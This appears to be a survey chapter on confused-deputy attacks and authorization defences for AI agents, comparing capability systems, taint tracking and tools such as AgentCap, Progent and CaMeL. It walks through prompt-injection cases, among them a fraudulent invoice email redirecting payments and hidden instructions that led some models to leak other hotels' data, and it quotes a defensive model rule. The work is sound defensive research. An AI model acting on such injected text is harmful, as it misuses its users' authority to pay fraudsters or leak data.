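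In the fourth program, the deputy reads a reference already stored in memory and writes the attacker's input to the location it points to. If that location is protected, the attacker can change it just by supplying the input. The capability check stops the attacker from retrieving the reference himself, but it allows the deputy to use it.

Suppose the bank once emailed a secret link to the shared mailbox that the assistant reads, and the link lets anyone who opens it change a standing order. An outsider can send mail to that mailbox but cannot read it. He writes that the standing order should now be €9,000 and that the link is in a message from March. The assistant finds the link and uses it to change the order.

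Rajani and colleagues call the first attack explicit designation, because the attacker gives the deputy the reference to misuse. In implicit designation, the deputy already holds the reference, and the attacker influences what the deputy writes to it. Capabilities prevent the first attack but none of the other three.

Most content cases involve implicit designation. The fraudulent invoice is one of them, even though the email names an account, because the account belongs to the fraudster and he is entitled to name it. If `pay_invoice` required a capability to deposit money in the payee's account, he could supply a genuine one. He lacks the authority to spend the company's money, but the assistant already has it.

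An email telling an agent to overwrite the payroll file would be explicit designation, because the sender names a file he isn't allowed to change. In a capability system, the name alone would not grant access to the file. But if the agent already held a capability to the whole folder containing it, the sender would only need to influence how the agent used that capability.

Explicit designation also occurs in the ordinary program around a model. *Type-Confusion Security* (Ren, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives an example using the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting AI applications to tools. A host program runs an action that the user has approved, then passes the result to a function that a third party has supplied for sending it to the conversation. An attacker instead supplies the host's own privileged function for running tools. The result contains a proposal for another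 action, which this function carries out without the user's approval.

Ren and colleagues label any call made through a supplied function as untrusted, and the privileged function accepts only trusted calls. They proved in Lean, a language in which a computer checks each step of a proof, that this check blocks untrusted calls to the privileged function in every program that follows their typing rules. The check protects the host from a substituted function, but it does not establish that an account number written by the model is the right one.

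### When capabilities are enough

A deputy can get a protected reference in three ways: its programmer wrote the reference into the code, the deputy reads it from memory, or the attacker passes it. The capability check blocks the third. Rajani and colleagues prove that capabilities prevent every confused deputy attack if the programmer also blocks the other two. The initial memory must contain no write reference to a location that the attacker wants to change but cannot write to himself. The deputy's code must contain none either, except in parts the programmer has deliberately exempted.

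The proof is short because these conditions ensure that, outside the exempted code, the deputy never holds a reference to a protected location of interest. It therefore never writes to one there, and the attacker's actions don't affect the final value.

The paper calls these restrictions "extremely strong" and concludes that they make the language useless for almost all practical purposes. A deputy exists to use authority that its users lack. Hardy's compiler has to write to the statistics file, and the office assistant has to make payments. Under the theorem, only exempted code could hold the references they need.

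Capabilities can still reduce what an attacker gains, for instance by letting the assistant pay only one supplier. The remaining authority is open to implicit designation. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), which describes a capability system for coding agents, acknowledges that an injection can cause an agent to misuse authority it was deliberately granted.

### Endorsement

The definition also rules out a part of the compiler that works as intended. In Rajani and colleagues' version, as in Miller and colleagues', the compiler writes the billing file itself. A user who submits a longer program gets a larger bill, so he influences a protected file that he cannot write to directly. To allow this, Rajani and colleagues let a programmer endorse regions of code, and they apply the definition only to stretches of the program that contain no endorsed region. In the compiler, the programmer endorses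 the code that calculates the bill but not the code that writes output to a place the user chooses, so an attack through the output code still counts.

Endorsement in this sense is a declaration of intent. The definition does not require the billing code to charge a fair price. If a user found a source text that made the code charge nothing, the program would still count as free from attacks.

Askarov and Myers (2011), in *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity*, analyse a stricter form, checked endorsement, in which a program tests an untrusted value and trusts it only if the test succeeds. Their example is a service that releases new data once an embargo has ended but lets the requester state the time of the request, so a requester could get the data early by stating a later time. With checked endorsement, the service first confirms that the stated time is in the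 past, and only then compares it with the embargo.

A similar test for the invoice would check the account number in the email against the one on record for Halvorsen. A match would be good reason to trust the number, but not the amount.

Checking only a value can miss where it came from. Cecchetti, Myers and Arden (2017), in *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control*, describe a sealed-bid auction in which Bob receives Alice's bid in a form he cannot read but can compute with. He submits "Alice's bid plus one", the auctioneer endorses it as Bob's own bid, and Bob always wins by the smallest margin. Cecchetti and colleagues therefore forbid a program to endorse information that its supposed provider could not have seen. An email asking the assistant to pay "whatever is left in the account" resembles Bob's bid, because the sender does not know the amount and the assistant fills it in.

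Even with this restriction, endorsement gives up the guarantee that untrusted input has no effect on trusted data. Ren and colleagues still regard endorsement as indispensable. An ordinary application, for example, must be able to change the operating system's state by making system calls.

### Tracking influence

Rajani and colleagues offer two alternatives to capabilities. Both keep the ordinary permission check and add a label to each value, recording the least trusted source that the program read to compute it. (Where two sources are not comparable, the label is their greatest lower bound in the order of authority.)

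Suppose unendorsed code writes a value with label $\ell_v$ to location $r$, using a reference with label $\ell_r$. If $O(r)$ is the owner of the location, the system allows the write only when

$$\ell_r \sqcap \ell_v \ge O(r)$$

where $\sqcap$ is the greatest lower bound. In `protected := input`, the value comes from a location that the attacker can write to, so $\ell_v$ is too low and the program halts. The check also catches the passed reference and the one already in memory, because the deputy read both from locations that the attacker can write to.

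This explicit-only tracking misses the controlled branch because the constants 41 and 42 come from the deputy's own code and carry the highest label. Its guarantee therefore still holds only if the deputy's unendorsed code contains no protected references of interest. The condition on memory is slightly weaker than the one for capabilities, because such references may be stored in locations the attacker can write to.

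Full provenance tracking adds a label $pc$ for whatever has influenced the program's path. When the program enters a branch or loop, the system lowers $pc$ to take account of the condition's label, and restores it when the program leaves. A write now requires

$$\ell_r \sqcap \ell_v \sqcap pc \ge O(r)$$

In the third program, the test on `input` lowers $pc$, so the deputy cannot write either constant. Rajani and colleagues prove that full tracking prevents all confused deputy attacks in unendorsed code, for every program and initial memory in their language. The table shows which mechanisms stop each attack.

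| Attack | Office-assistant version | Ordinary permission check | Capabilities | Explicit-only tracking | Full tracking |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Passed reference | Employee names the payroll account | No | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Controlled value | Email supplies the account number | No | No | Yes | Yes |
| Controlled branch | Email claims that the director approved | No | No | No | Yes |
| Reference already in memory | Email points to an old bank link | No | No | Yes | Yes |

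Full tracking takes more computation and halts some harmless programs. It stops the third program even if no attacker is present, because it forbids less trusted data from influencing more trusted data at all, which is stricter than the definition requires. Every output of a language model can depend on its whole context, so the same rule would block each payment after the first outside email unless somebody endorsed it.

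Gallo (2026), in *Full Provenance on the COSS Causal Axis*, reaches a similar difficulty by tracking authority. Gallo treats all four attacks as chains of causes leading from a request to an effect, whether the link is a passed reference, a copied value, a branch or something stored earlier. Under Gallo's rule, an event $e$ carries no more authority than all its immediate causes have in common:

$$C(e) \subseteq \bigcap_{p \in \mathrm{Pred}(e)} C(p)$$

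Here $C(e)$ is the authority available at the event and $\mathrm{Pred}(e)$ is the set of its immediate causes. If the clerk's request carries permission to pay and the supplier's email carries none, they share no authority, and the rule blocks the payment even when the invoice is genuine. To pay it, someone has to authorize the combination as a separate step, which Gallo's theorem does not cover. The theorem also assumes that the system has recorded every relevant cause.

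### Writing and secrecy

Rajani and colleagues' theorems cover only what an attacker can change. The programming language they study lets any code read through any read reference it holds, so the theorems do not apply to the employee who wants to see his colleagues' salaries, or to an email that gets an agent to send out customer data.

Hardy's remedy does extend to reading. If `look_up_record` required a capability from the person asking, the sales employee would have none for the salary table. Capabilities help less when the agent is authorized both to read the data and to send messages. *DelegateGuard* proves that a capability monitor that ignores the content and quantity of data cannot prevent leaks to an authorized destination that outsiders can see.

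A capability system can prevent data leaks by withholding either the data or the means of sending it out, but only if capabilities do not spread from one program to another. In 1984, Boebert argued that they do. In his example, a program with low clearance stores its capability to write to a low-security file in that file. A program with high clearance reads the file, obtains the capability, and can then copy secrets into the file, where the first program can read them.

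Miller and colleagues reply that this attack works only where capabilities can travel wherever data can. Most capability systems keep the two apart, so the high-clearance program could read the file's data without obtaining the capability. A language model's context does not separate them. The secret bank link in the shared mailbox works as a capability for anyone who has the text, and once the assistant has read it, the model can copy it into a reply. To prevent this, the program around the model has to hold the capabilities and let the model refer to them only indirectly.

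## Limiting what each tool call can reach

An assistant that pays invoices needs permission to make payments, and an attacker can influence how it uses that permission. A developer can still limit what the permission covers. The general rule is the principle of least privilege, which Saltzer and Schroeder set out in 1975 and under which a program holds only the permissions its work requires.

Developers often don't limit tool access when they set up agents. Noyan, in *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents*, writes that companies typically give an agent every tool its role might need and keep all of them available for every task. An office assistant therefore has access to the bank account even while it looks up a phone number. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* lists five points where access can be limited: which tools the model can see, whether the current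 step needs the tool the model chose, which argument values are acceptable, how much data a tool returns, and how much authority a sub-agent receives.

### Taking the choice away from the model

Baig and colleagues first remove the `hotel_id` argument, which had let a hotel manager's agent reach other hotels' records. The model calls `get_reservations(limit)` instead of `get_reservations(hotel_id, limit)`, and the server determines the hotel from a signed credential. The model therefore cannot request another hotel's records.

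They tested the idea in 373 trials with eight model configurations from five providers. Each agent worked for a user whose account covered three hotels and who was busy with one of them. The trials used three versions of the tool:

- **With the argument.** The model names a hotel, and the server checks that the user's account covers it.
- **Without the argument.** The server takes the hotel from the session.
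- **With the argument and a rule.** A standing instruction also tells the model never to retrieve another hotel's data, whatever any text asks.

Some requests were harmless. Others used a plausible pretext, with the user asking for the same figures for a second hotel and saying he needed them for a comparison. The remaining attacks used a fake system directive or an instruction hidden in a guest's note. Baig and colleagues counted a leak whenever the server's log showed that a tool had returned another hotel's rows, regardless of what the agent said it had done.

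When the tool had the argument, agents tried to fetch the second hotel's figures in 26 of the 41 pretext trials, and the server returned them in all 26. The 15 trials without an attempt all used GPT-5.6 models. Claude Opus 5 resisted all 26 fake directives and hidden instructions it encountered with this version of the tool, but it fetched the other hotel's data in all 18 of its pretext trials. Several agents said they might not have clearance but fetched the data anyway.

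"Leak" may not be the right word, since the user's account did cover the second hotel and managers have good reasons to compare hotels. But the server could not have distinguished the manager's own request from one planted through an email, because both arrive as the same call with the same credential.

Without the argument, no call naming another hotel succeeded in the 56 pretext trials. But in 12 of them the agent got the other hotel's rows by altering the scope outside the tool, so a deployment has to sign the scope cryptographically.

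The standing instruction also did well, with no leaks in 33 pretext trials, though the true rate could still be as high as about 10%. Fifteen of those trials used the GPT-5.6 models, which had not leaked under the pretext even without the instruction, so the evidence that it helps comes from the 18 trials with Claude, where leaks fell from 18 to none.

The effect is large, but it depends on how the model behaves. The instruction has to be present and well worded, and it has to outweigh any business reason given in the request. Baig and colleagues did not test the instruction under the pretext on the GPT-5.4 mini and Gemini 3.1 Pro configurations, which had obeyed the fake directive in every trial with the plain argument. A company that changes models would have to measure the rate again. Removing the argument gives the same result with any model, as long as the agent has no other way to reach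 the data.

The deployed design gives weaker protection than the experiment might suggest, because it limits an agent only to what the user's credential covers, which for some managers is a whole portfolio of hotels. When a tool has to work on a single hotel, the model chooses that hotel in an earlier call from a list of permitted ones, and an email can influence that choice too. To confine the agent to one hotel, the user would have to pick it on a screen or log in with a credential for that hotel alone.

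The limit also has to apply to every table a query uses. In the hotel database that Baig and colleagues studied, 15.72% of the rows in one table pointed to another hotel's entry in a shared register. Every such entry they inspected held a name and a telephone number. A query that filtered the first table but not the register would have returned these entries, even though the model never named another hotel.

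The office assistant could use the same remedy. If `pay_invoice` took only an invoice number, and ordinary code looked up Halvorsen's account in the supplier records, the model would have no field in which to enter the fraudster's account number. The model would still choose which invoice to pay, and the clerk would need another way to record a supplier's genuine change of bank. Other arguments have to stay, such as the message in a tool that sends mail, because writing the message is often the reason for using a model.

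### Checking each call

When the model must supply a value, a program outside the model can check it before the tool runs. Mellafe Zuvic, in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (June 2026), looked for such a check in the public source code of three toolkits that developers use to build agents. (The "capability gates" of the title are lists of available tools, not capabilities in Hardy's sense.)

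None of the three performs this per-call authorization by default:

- **LangChain and LangGraph** look up the tool by the name the model wrote, usually check that the arguments have the right types, and run it. A developer can add a step in which a person approves the call.
- **LlamaIndex** checks that a tool of that name exists and passes on the model's arguments.
- **Stripe's Agent Toolkit**, which handles payments, restricts the available actions and uses an access key with limited scope. Within those limits, it forwards the amount, the customer and the payment reference as the model wrote them.

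A type check can reject an account number that contains a smiley, but it cannot determine whose account it is. Mellafe Zuvic describes the missing ownership check as a design decision that leaves this check to whoever builds the agent, and does not report it as a vulnerability. The audit covered only public code, so Stripe's remote servers may perform additional checks.

To show the consequence, Mellafe Zuvic connected LangChain to a mock merchant system and fed it a fixed model output that redirected the merchant's payouts to an attacker's account. LangChain made the change. The same call failed when it first went through ScopeGate, Mellafe Zuvic's own checking program, because the account was not on the merchant's list. For a payment by the office assistant, ScopeGate would go through these steps:

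1. **Tool.** If the policy does not list `pay_invoice`, refuse. This also catches misspelled names and tools that the model has discovered by itself.
2. **Values.** For each argument that has a list of permitted values, refuse anything not on the list. The fraudulent Halvorsen account fails here.
3. **Amount.** Refuse unless the amount is a finite number between zero and the ceiling.
4. **Repeats.** Refuse if the call needs an idempotency key and the surrounding program has not supplied one. The key is an identifier by which the payment service can recognize a second copy of the same request.
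5. **Default.** Allow the call only if it has passed every step, and treat any error during the checks as a refusal.

Step 3 requires the amount to lie inside the range. An earlier version of ScopeGate instead refused amounts greater than the ceiling, and a payment of NaN ("not a number") got through because, in most programming languages, this special value is neither greater nor smaller than any number. The range check refuses NaN.

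These steps do not stop every attack. An argument without a list goes unchecked. The ceiling applies to each call separately, so the procedure allows ten payments just below it. A false invoice from a supplier whose account is on the list also passes if the amount is low enough.

Mellafe Zuvic insists that the policy come from outside the model. An email can change the account number in the model's proposed call, but it can't change the list of verified accounts if an operator wrote that list and the model can't edit it. If the model could add to the list, the same email could change both, and the check would compare the attacker's number with itself. Under this rule, no part of the policy may derive from model output, including when someone drafts it in advance or updates it later.

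The separation also helps because ScopeGate checks only the call, so it makes no difference whether a bad call came from an injected email or from a model that somebody tampered with during training.

In tests, ScopeGate blocked all 48 hand-written attempts to bypass it, which used tricks such as look-alike letters and invisible characters. A language model that was given the reason for each refusal and tried again for 40 rounds produced 29 unauthorized calls, and none succeeded. All ten legitimate calls went through. These results mostly confirm that the program follows its rules, since it is designed to refuse any account that is missing from a list. They provide little evidence about the harder task of keeping the list correct. For example, a new supplier's first legitimate invoice would fail until somebody had verified the account.

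### Tokens that holders can only narrow

An operator's list usually stays the same across tasks, but the permissions an agent needs vary. A token can carry permission for a single job, and an agent that delegates part of the job can pass on only part of that permission. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) uses the traditional name for this, attenuation. For example, someone who can read and write a whole file system can pass on a reference that only allows reading one directory.

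Birgisson and colleagues brought attenuation to web credentials in 2014 with macaroons. A macaroon consists of an identifier, a list of restrictions called caveats, and a signature. The service that issues it computes the first signature from a secret key $k$ and the identifier. Anyone who holds the macaroon can add a caveat $c_i$ and replace the signature:

$$\sigma_0 = \mathrm{HMAC}(k, \mathit{id}), \qquad \sigma_i = \mathrm{HMAC}(\sigma_{i-1}, c_i)$$

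HMAC is a function that turns a key and a message into a short signature, from which nobody can feasibly recover the key. Each signature is the key for the next one, and the holder passes on only the latest.

Suppose the office assistant holds a macaroon for the shared mailbox. Before giving it to a sub-agent, the assistant adds the caveats "only messages from Halvorsen" and "only until 5 p.m.", which it can do without contacting the mail service. The sub-agent can add further caveats but cannot remove these, because it would need an earlier signature that it never received. When the sub-agent presents the macaroon, the mail service recomputes the chain from $k$ and checks that every caveat holds.

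Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, build a similar scheme for tool calls. Their system, AgentCap, gives the agent no standing permission to use a tool. A wrapper around the tools submits each proposed call to a policy engine, which either refuses or issues a signed token. A gateway checks the token before passing the call on. The table explains the token's thirteen fields and includes any values set by the paper's sample rule for bank payments.

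| Field | Meaning | Sample payment rule |
|---|---|---|
| $u$, $s$ | Agent and session that may use the token | The requesting agent and its session |
| $a$, $r$ | Action and resource | Write, to bank transfers |
| $i$ | Declared purpose | Paying a bill or sending a payment |
| $q$, $e$ | Times of issue and expiry | 30 seconds apart |
| $b$ | Number of calls allowed | 1 |
| $P$ | Permissions the agent must already hold | Reading the balance |
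| $G$ | Groups that rule out dangerous combinations | Financial writes |
| $\theta$ | Agent's trust score at issue | At least 0.8 |
| $j$, $\rho$ | Token's identifier and the record of the decision | Set at issue |

Before issuing a token, the engine confirms that it has not shut the agent off, that the tool is in its catalogue, and that sensitive values such as the payee do not come solely from untrusted text. It then checks the purpose, the trust score, the required permissions and the forbidden combinations. The purpose check only ties the token to one of the purposes the policy allows for that tool. It is not evidence of good intentions, because the model declares the purpose itself.

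The thirteen fields do not include the payee or the amount, so the gateway relies on the wrapper, which Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao trust, to send the tool the same arguments that the policy engine approved.

The trust score starts at 0.8 and loses 30% of its value after each refused or abnormal call. After three such calls it is 0.274, and AgentCap revokes all the agent's permissions. The default numbers look harsh when combined with the sample payment rule, which requires a score of at least 0.8. One refusal lowers the score to 0.56, and each normal call closes only 1% of the remaining gap to 1, so the agent would need 79 normal calls before it could pay again. An outsider whose email provoked a single refused call could stop the company's payments until the agent had made those calls.

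When one agent delegates a token $\tau$ to another, the new token $\tau'$ must satisfy

$$a' = a, \quad r' = r, \quad b' \le b, \quad e' \le e, \quad d' < d$$

where $d$ is the number of further handovers allowed. The action and resource stay the same, the budget and lifetime cannot grow, and the chain of handovers has to end. The gateway checks the chain from the last token back to the first and refuses the call if anyone has revoked a link. AgentCap is less flexible than a macaroon in one respect, since an agent with a token for a folder cannot pass on permission for just one file in it.

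This rule only partly solves the case in which an agent asked to summarize invoices forwards a payment request to a finance agent. The first agent has only read permission, so that is all it can delegate. But the finance agent can request its own payment token from the policy engine. Whether it gets one depends on the other checks, above all on where the payee's account number came from.

### How much AgentCap prevents

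Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on AgentDojo and InjecAgent, two benchmarks of injection attacks on tool-using agents. They used GPT-4o, from 2024, and the newer GPT-5.4. Cells with two figures give the result without AgentCap, then with it. Task success is the share of the user's own tasks that the agent completed.

| Benchmark and model | Attack success rate | Task success under attack | Change in task success without an attack |
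|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% → 5.09% | 73.61% → 74.88% | −3.1 points |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% → 0% | 75.68% → 75.04% | −7.2 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% → 8.63% | 74.10% → 69.92% | −3.9 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% → 0% | 72.96% → 69.92% | −2.0 points |

Three kinds of attack still worked on GPT-4o. The first only made the model write certain text to the user, which no check on tool calls can prevent. The second changed an argument that the policy did not protect, and the third delivered a value through a field that the policy had not marked as untrusted.

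Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote the policies from the tools' descriptions and the benchmark's user tasks, and did not change them after seeing results. The policies were not tailored to a particular model, so the gaps that attackers used against GPT-4o were presumably open with GPT-5.4 too. In that case, the zeros would be partly due to GPT-5.4's own resistance, and a better attack might get through the same gaps.

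Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao did not test AgentCap against an adaptive attacker and leave that to future work. Prompt-based defences also did very well against AgentDojo's fixed attacks, then failed almost completely once attackers adapted. AgentCap has an advantage over them, because rewording an email does not help an attacker if the payee's account fails a fixed check. The attacker would instead have to find unprotected arguments and unmarked fields, and the benchmark does not measure how hard that is. Each condition also ran only once, so small differences in the table may be noise.

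People make mistakes when they write such policies by hand, and a program can find some of these mistakes in advance. AgentCap's analyser found that nobody could ever delete a customer under one customer-service policy, because the permission required beforehand conflicted with a rule about forbidden combinations. It also lists pairs of permissions that together would let an agent read sensitive data and send it out.

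### Who writes the policy

All these checks enforce whatever policy they receive, and *DelegateGuard* measures what happens when that policy is wrong. In its system, a trusted adapter turns the user's task into a first grant, using templates for each kind of work. The grant specifies a purpose, the kinds of data the agent may handle, the operations it may perform, the destinations it may send to, and how often it may delegate. Sub-agents can receive no more than this, and cancelling a grant also cancels everything derived from it.

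None of 45 attacks succeeded when the grant covered only what the task needed. Adding one external web address to the grant, as a developer might for convenience, allowed 30 of them to succeed. In the other 15, a sub-agent tried to act after the user had cancelled the task, and these attacks still failed. Leaving out the permission to transmit data blocked all 45 harmless tasks. People complain as soon as an overly narrow policy stops their work, but a developer may not learn that a policy is too broad until after an attack.

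Even a well-chosen grant did not prevent every leak in a separate test, where a small open model worked over several turns. The monitor reduced the number of attacked workflows that leaked data from 38 of 45 to nine. All nine were in code review, where the agent's legitimate output was a comment that outsiders could read.

Templates suit work that a company can describe in advance. General assistants receive requests that nobody foresaw, and the services they use are large. Slack alone offers 247 operations. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) therefore has a language model write a policy for each request. The policy is a set of rules about tools and their arguments, such as allowing Slack messages only to Alice. An ordinary program checks every call against the rules and refuses any call that no rule allows.

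The model writes the first policy from the user's request, before the agent has read any outside text. But the request often doesn't show which tools the task needs. If the user asks the agent to do whatever is on the to-do list in Alice's email, the agent has to open the email to find out. Progent therefore lets the model revise the policy as the agent works. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that hostile text in a tool's result may cause such a revision to loosen the policy.

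Shi and colleagues respond to this risk with a solver, a program that can settle logical questions about all possible calls at once. If $A(P)$ is the set of calls that policy $P$ allows, Progent applies a new policy $P'$ automatically only when

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

Any update that would allow even one more call needs approval. Permissions can therefore only shrink between approvals, even if an attacker controls the model that writes the policy.

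On AgentDojo, Progent reduced the attack success rate for GPT-4o from 39.9% to 1.0%. In this main experiment, Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically to imitate a careless user, so the low rate reflects how well the model wrote policies and doesn't show that the solver works. The rate was 2.5% with the first policy and no updates, and zero when a careful person reviewed the first policy and each expansion. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so the reviewer had few to read.

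Shi and colleagues also tried three attacks aimed at the policy-writing model, including one that added a one-sentence request to permit the attacker's tools. They report that the attacks raised the success rate only marginally, again with automatic approval.

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao later ran Progent on their own version of AgentDojo, which restored two travel tasks that Shi and colleagues had left out. In these tasks, the attacker steers the agent towards one of several legitimate hotels. Shi and colleagues consider such attacks unrealistic because someone who controls a hotel's listing can rewrite it. Progent let through roughly 5% of attacks, about the same share as AgentCap. Without an attack, it completed 68% of tasks, compared with 78% for AgentCap, largely because the model had often restricted arguments to the values it predicted, which blocked other legitimate values.

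Mellafe Zuvic's rule would exclude Progent because Progent's policy is model output. That seems too strict for the first policy, which the model writes without seeing any outside text, but it is a good argument against approving later expansions automatically. *Authority Is Not a String* proposes a compromise for coding agents, in which the program around the model sets an upper limit on permissions for the whole task before any text from the code repository is available, and sub-agents can only receive permissions within that limit.

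*MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) takes its policy from the services the agent uses. Gmail, Slack and similar services already publish scopes, which are groups of operations that a user can permit together. Several scopes may cover the same operation, as they do for 24 of Google Calendar's 37 operations, so choosing the smallest sufficient set is an optimization problem. MiniScope gives each scope a weight based on how many operations it allows, and a solver finds the set with the lowest total weight that covers the agent's plan. The user then approves or refuses that set.

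Even when Zhu and colleagues gave language models the plan and the full list of scopes, the models chose sets that allowed on average between 1.03 and 2.19 times as many operations as MiniScope's, depending on the model and the task. Commercial products also requested too much access. ChatGPT's Gmail connector requested scopes covering 50 operations when its tools needed only 32, and the extra ones included changing and deleting mail.

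Counting operations is a crude measure of danger because reading a label and deleting a mailbox count the same, but a developer can use a different measure. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) adds that Zhu and colleagues do not discuss whether the best set is unique. If two sets tie for best and each permits something the other doesn't, the solver's choice between them is arbitrary.

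The greater weakness is that scopes do not restrict a call's arguments. If an email tells the agent to delete messages when it has permission only to read them, MiniScope has to ask the user, who may notice the attack. But if the email changes the account number in a payment that the scope already allows, MiniScope lets the payment through. Zhu and colleagues chose this level of detail because asking users about every recipient and file would tire them. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) makes the same criticism of scopes and derives permission for particular values from the wording of the user's task. It reports that its system allowed every harmless AgentDojo task and blocked every attack, but a vaguely worded task can still produce too broad a permission.

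| System | Source of the policy | How permissions can grow during a task |
|---|---|---|
| ScopeGate | Operator's configuration | They cannot |
| AgentCap | Developer's rules for each kind of work | The agent requests more tokens within the rules |
| DelegateGuard | Trusted adapter, using templates | The adapter issues a new grant |
| Progent | Language model, from the user's request | A person or an automatic setting approves |
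| MiniScope | Services' published scopes and a solver | The user approves |

The systems also differ in whether they protect against the user. Progent assumes that the user is honest. If the sales employee asks for everyone's salary, a policy that allows only what his task needs will still let the agent read the salary table. A company can add fixed rules to Progent that no task can override, but a rule against reading salaries would also stop the payroll staff. MiniScope largely avoids the problem because the agent works through the user's own accounts, and the sales employee's account has no access to salaries. With a shared database login such as the office assistant's, the policy would have to depend on who is asking.

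## Tracking where data came from

A list of approved accounts can stop the fraudulent payment to Halvorsen's supposed new account, but somebody has to compile and update it. The program around the model can instead check where an account number came from, allowing the payment if the clerk typed the number and refusing it if the number appears only in a stranger's email.

This check needs a record of where every value came from. Ordinary programs can keep one by taint tracking, and Dorothy Denning published a general theory of this in 1976. Rajani and colleagues use a form of taint tracking that labels each value with its least trusted source.

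### Labels, and what a model does to them

In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) apply taint tracking to agents using FIDES, a system they built at Microsoft. Its simplest integrity labels are trusted and untrusted. If ordinary code puts the words "Pay to" in front of an account number from an email, the result is untrusted, and it stays untrusted when the code trims, copies or reformats it.

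FIDES also labels each value with the people who may read it, so it can address leaks, which Rajani and colleagues' theorems don't cover. If Anna, Ben and Carla may read one document, and Ben, Carla and David may read another, only Ben and Carla may read text derived from both. Before the agent sends a message, FIDES can check that every recipient may read its contents.

In ordinary code, each instruction names its inputs, which keeps the labels precise. Nobody can reliably tell which parts of a language model's context shaped its output, so Costa and colleagues give the output the combined label of everything in the context. Once the office assistant has read an outside email, every tool-call argument it writes is labeled untrusted, including an account number the clerk typed.

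In tests on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, refusing consequential tool calls from untrusted contexts stopped every attack counted as genuine. It also reduced the share of tasks completed. An ordinary agent completed 98.8% of banking tasks and 93.3% of Slack tasks, but with this restriction the figures fell to 37.5% and 20%.

Cai, Wen, Tang and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, try to recover the finer distinctions from an agent's log. Their program, NeuroTaint, compares meanings, so it can recognize text that the model has paraphrased. It also tests for influence that leaves no trace in the wording, by replacing a source with neutral text and checking whether the model would still make the call. On their own benchmark of 400 scenarios, it found 93.5% of the flows from untrusted sources to sensitive tools, and 92.1% of its alarms were correct. That is useful for investigating an incident,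 but the analysis runs after the payment has gone out. If a company used it to block calls, an attacker would look for text that it fails to catch.

### A planner that never reads the mail

The label on the planning model's context stays trusted if untrusted text never enters it. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting the work between two models for this reason. A planner sees the user's request and can call tools. A reader sees untrusted text and has no tools. Between them sits a controller, which is ordinary software. When the clerk asks for a summary of an email, they work as follows:

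1. The controller gives the planner the clerk's request, and the planner writes a call to `read_mail`.
2. The controller fetches the email and stores it as `$VAR1`. It tells the planner only that name.
3. The planner writes a request to summarize `$VAR1`. The controller inserts the email's text and sends it to the reader.
4. The controller stores the reader's summary as `$VAR2`, and the planner writes an instruction to display `$VAR2`.
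5. The controller replaces the name with the summary and shows it to the clerk.

An instruction hidden in the email can make the reader write a false summary, but the reader cannot send money and the planner never receives the instruction. Willison lets the planner receive an answer from the reader only if the controller has confirmed that the answer is one of a fixed set of categories.

He called his own solution "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and because a single mistake that lets text through to the planner defeats it.

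Researchers at Google DeepMind later found another weakness, as Willison explained in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025). Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document and says Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The planner has the reader extract the address, but an attacker who can write in the notes has put his own there. The assistant then follows the planner's steps exactly and sends the document to the attacker. *SPA* (2026) points out that such an attack needs no malicious instruction. A false account number in an invoice is enough, and a detector that searches for commands will miss it.

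The DeepMind researchers' system, CaMeL, adds taint tracking to the split. Its planner writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python before the agent reads anything. A special interpreter runs the program and records, for each variable, which sources it derives from and who may read it. Before a tool call, the interpreter checks these tags against rules, such as one that allows email only to trusted recipients. (The designers call the tags capabilities, though a tag only describes a value and does not by itself authorize anything.)

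FIDES lets the planner choose one step at a time. It hides part of a tool's result behind a variable only if showing that part would give the planner's context a more restrictive label. The planner can open a hidden value, but its context then takes on the value's label. *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) extends the approach to web pages.

With its checks on, FIDES completed 52.5% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 47.6% of its Slack tasks, so hiding values recovered part of what the ordinary agent had lost. It completed 41% of travel tasks, against 73% for the ordinary agent with checks, because few of those tasks need a restricted call and GPT-4o often misused the variables. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks.

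No genuine attack succeeded, but this is less impressive than it sounds because Costa and colleagues marked the fields that AgentDojo's attacks use as untrusted. A company has to label its data without knowing which fields attackers will choose.

FIDES also assumes that the user, the developer's instructions and the tool descriptions are trustworthy. *SPA* notes that tool names and descriptions normally go into the planner's input, where a malicious one can bias the plan before the agent has read any mail. Because FIDES trusts the user, it would not block the salary request unless the company labels the salary table with its permitted readers and checks replies as well as tool calls. FIDES does not check replies by default.

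### When the clerk names the account

Suppose the clerk writes, "Pay this morning's Halvorsen invoice to account 4417." A planner like CaMeL's might produce this plan:

```python
mail = read_mail("Halvorsen Paper")
amount = ask_reader("What is the amount due?", mail)
pay_invoice(account="4417", amount=amount)
```

The fraudster may demand payment to a different account, but no line of the plan takes an account number from the email. In an ordinary agent, one model reads everything and might still write the fraudster's number into the tool call. A provenance check would then block the payment, because that number appears only in the email.

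The amount does come from the email, so a rule that every argument must be trusted would also block this honest payment. The rule has to distinguish between arguments. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents a monitor called PACT that does this. It gives each argument a role, such as a destination, a command, a password or plain content, and each role has its own minimum level of trust. If a user asks the model to email a summary of a web page, the page may determine the body of the message but not the recipient.

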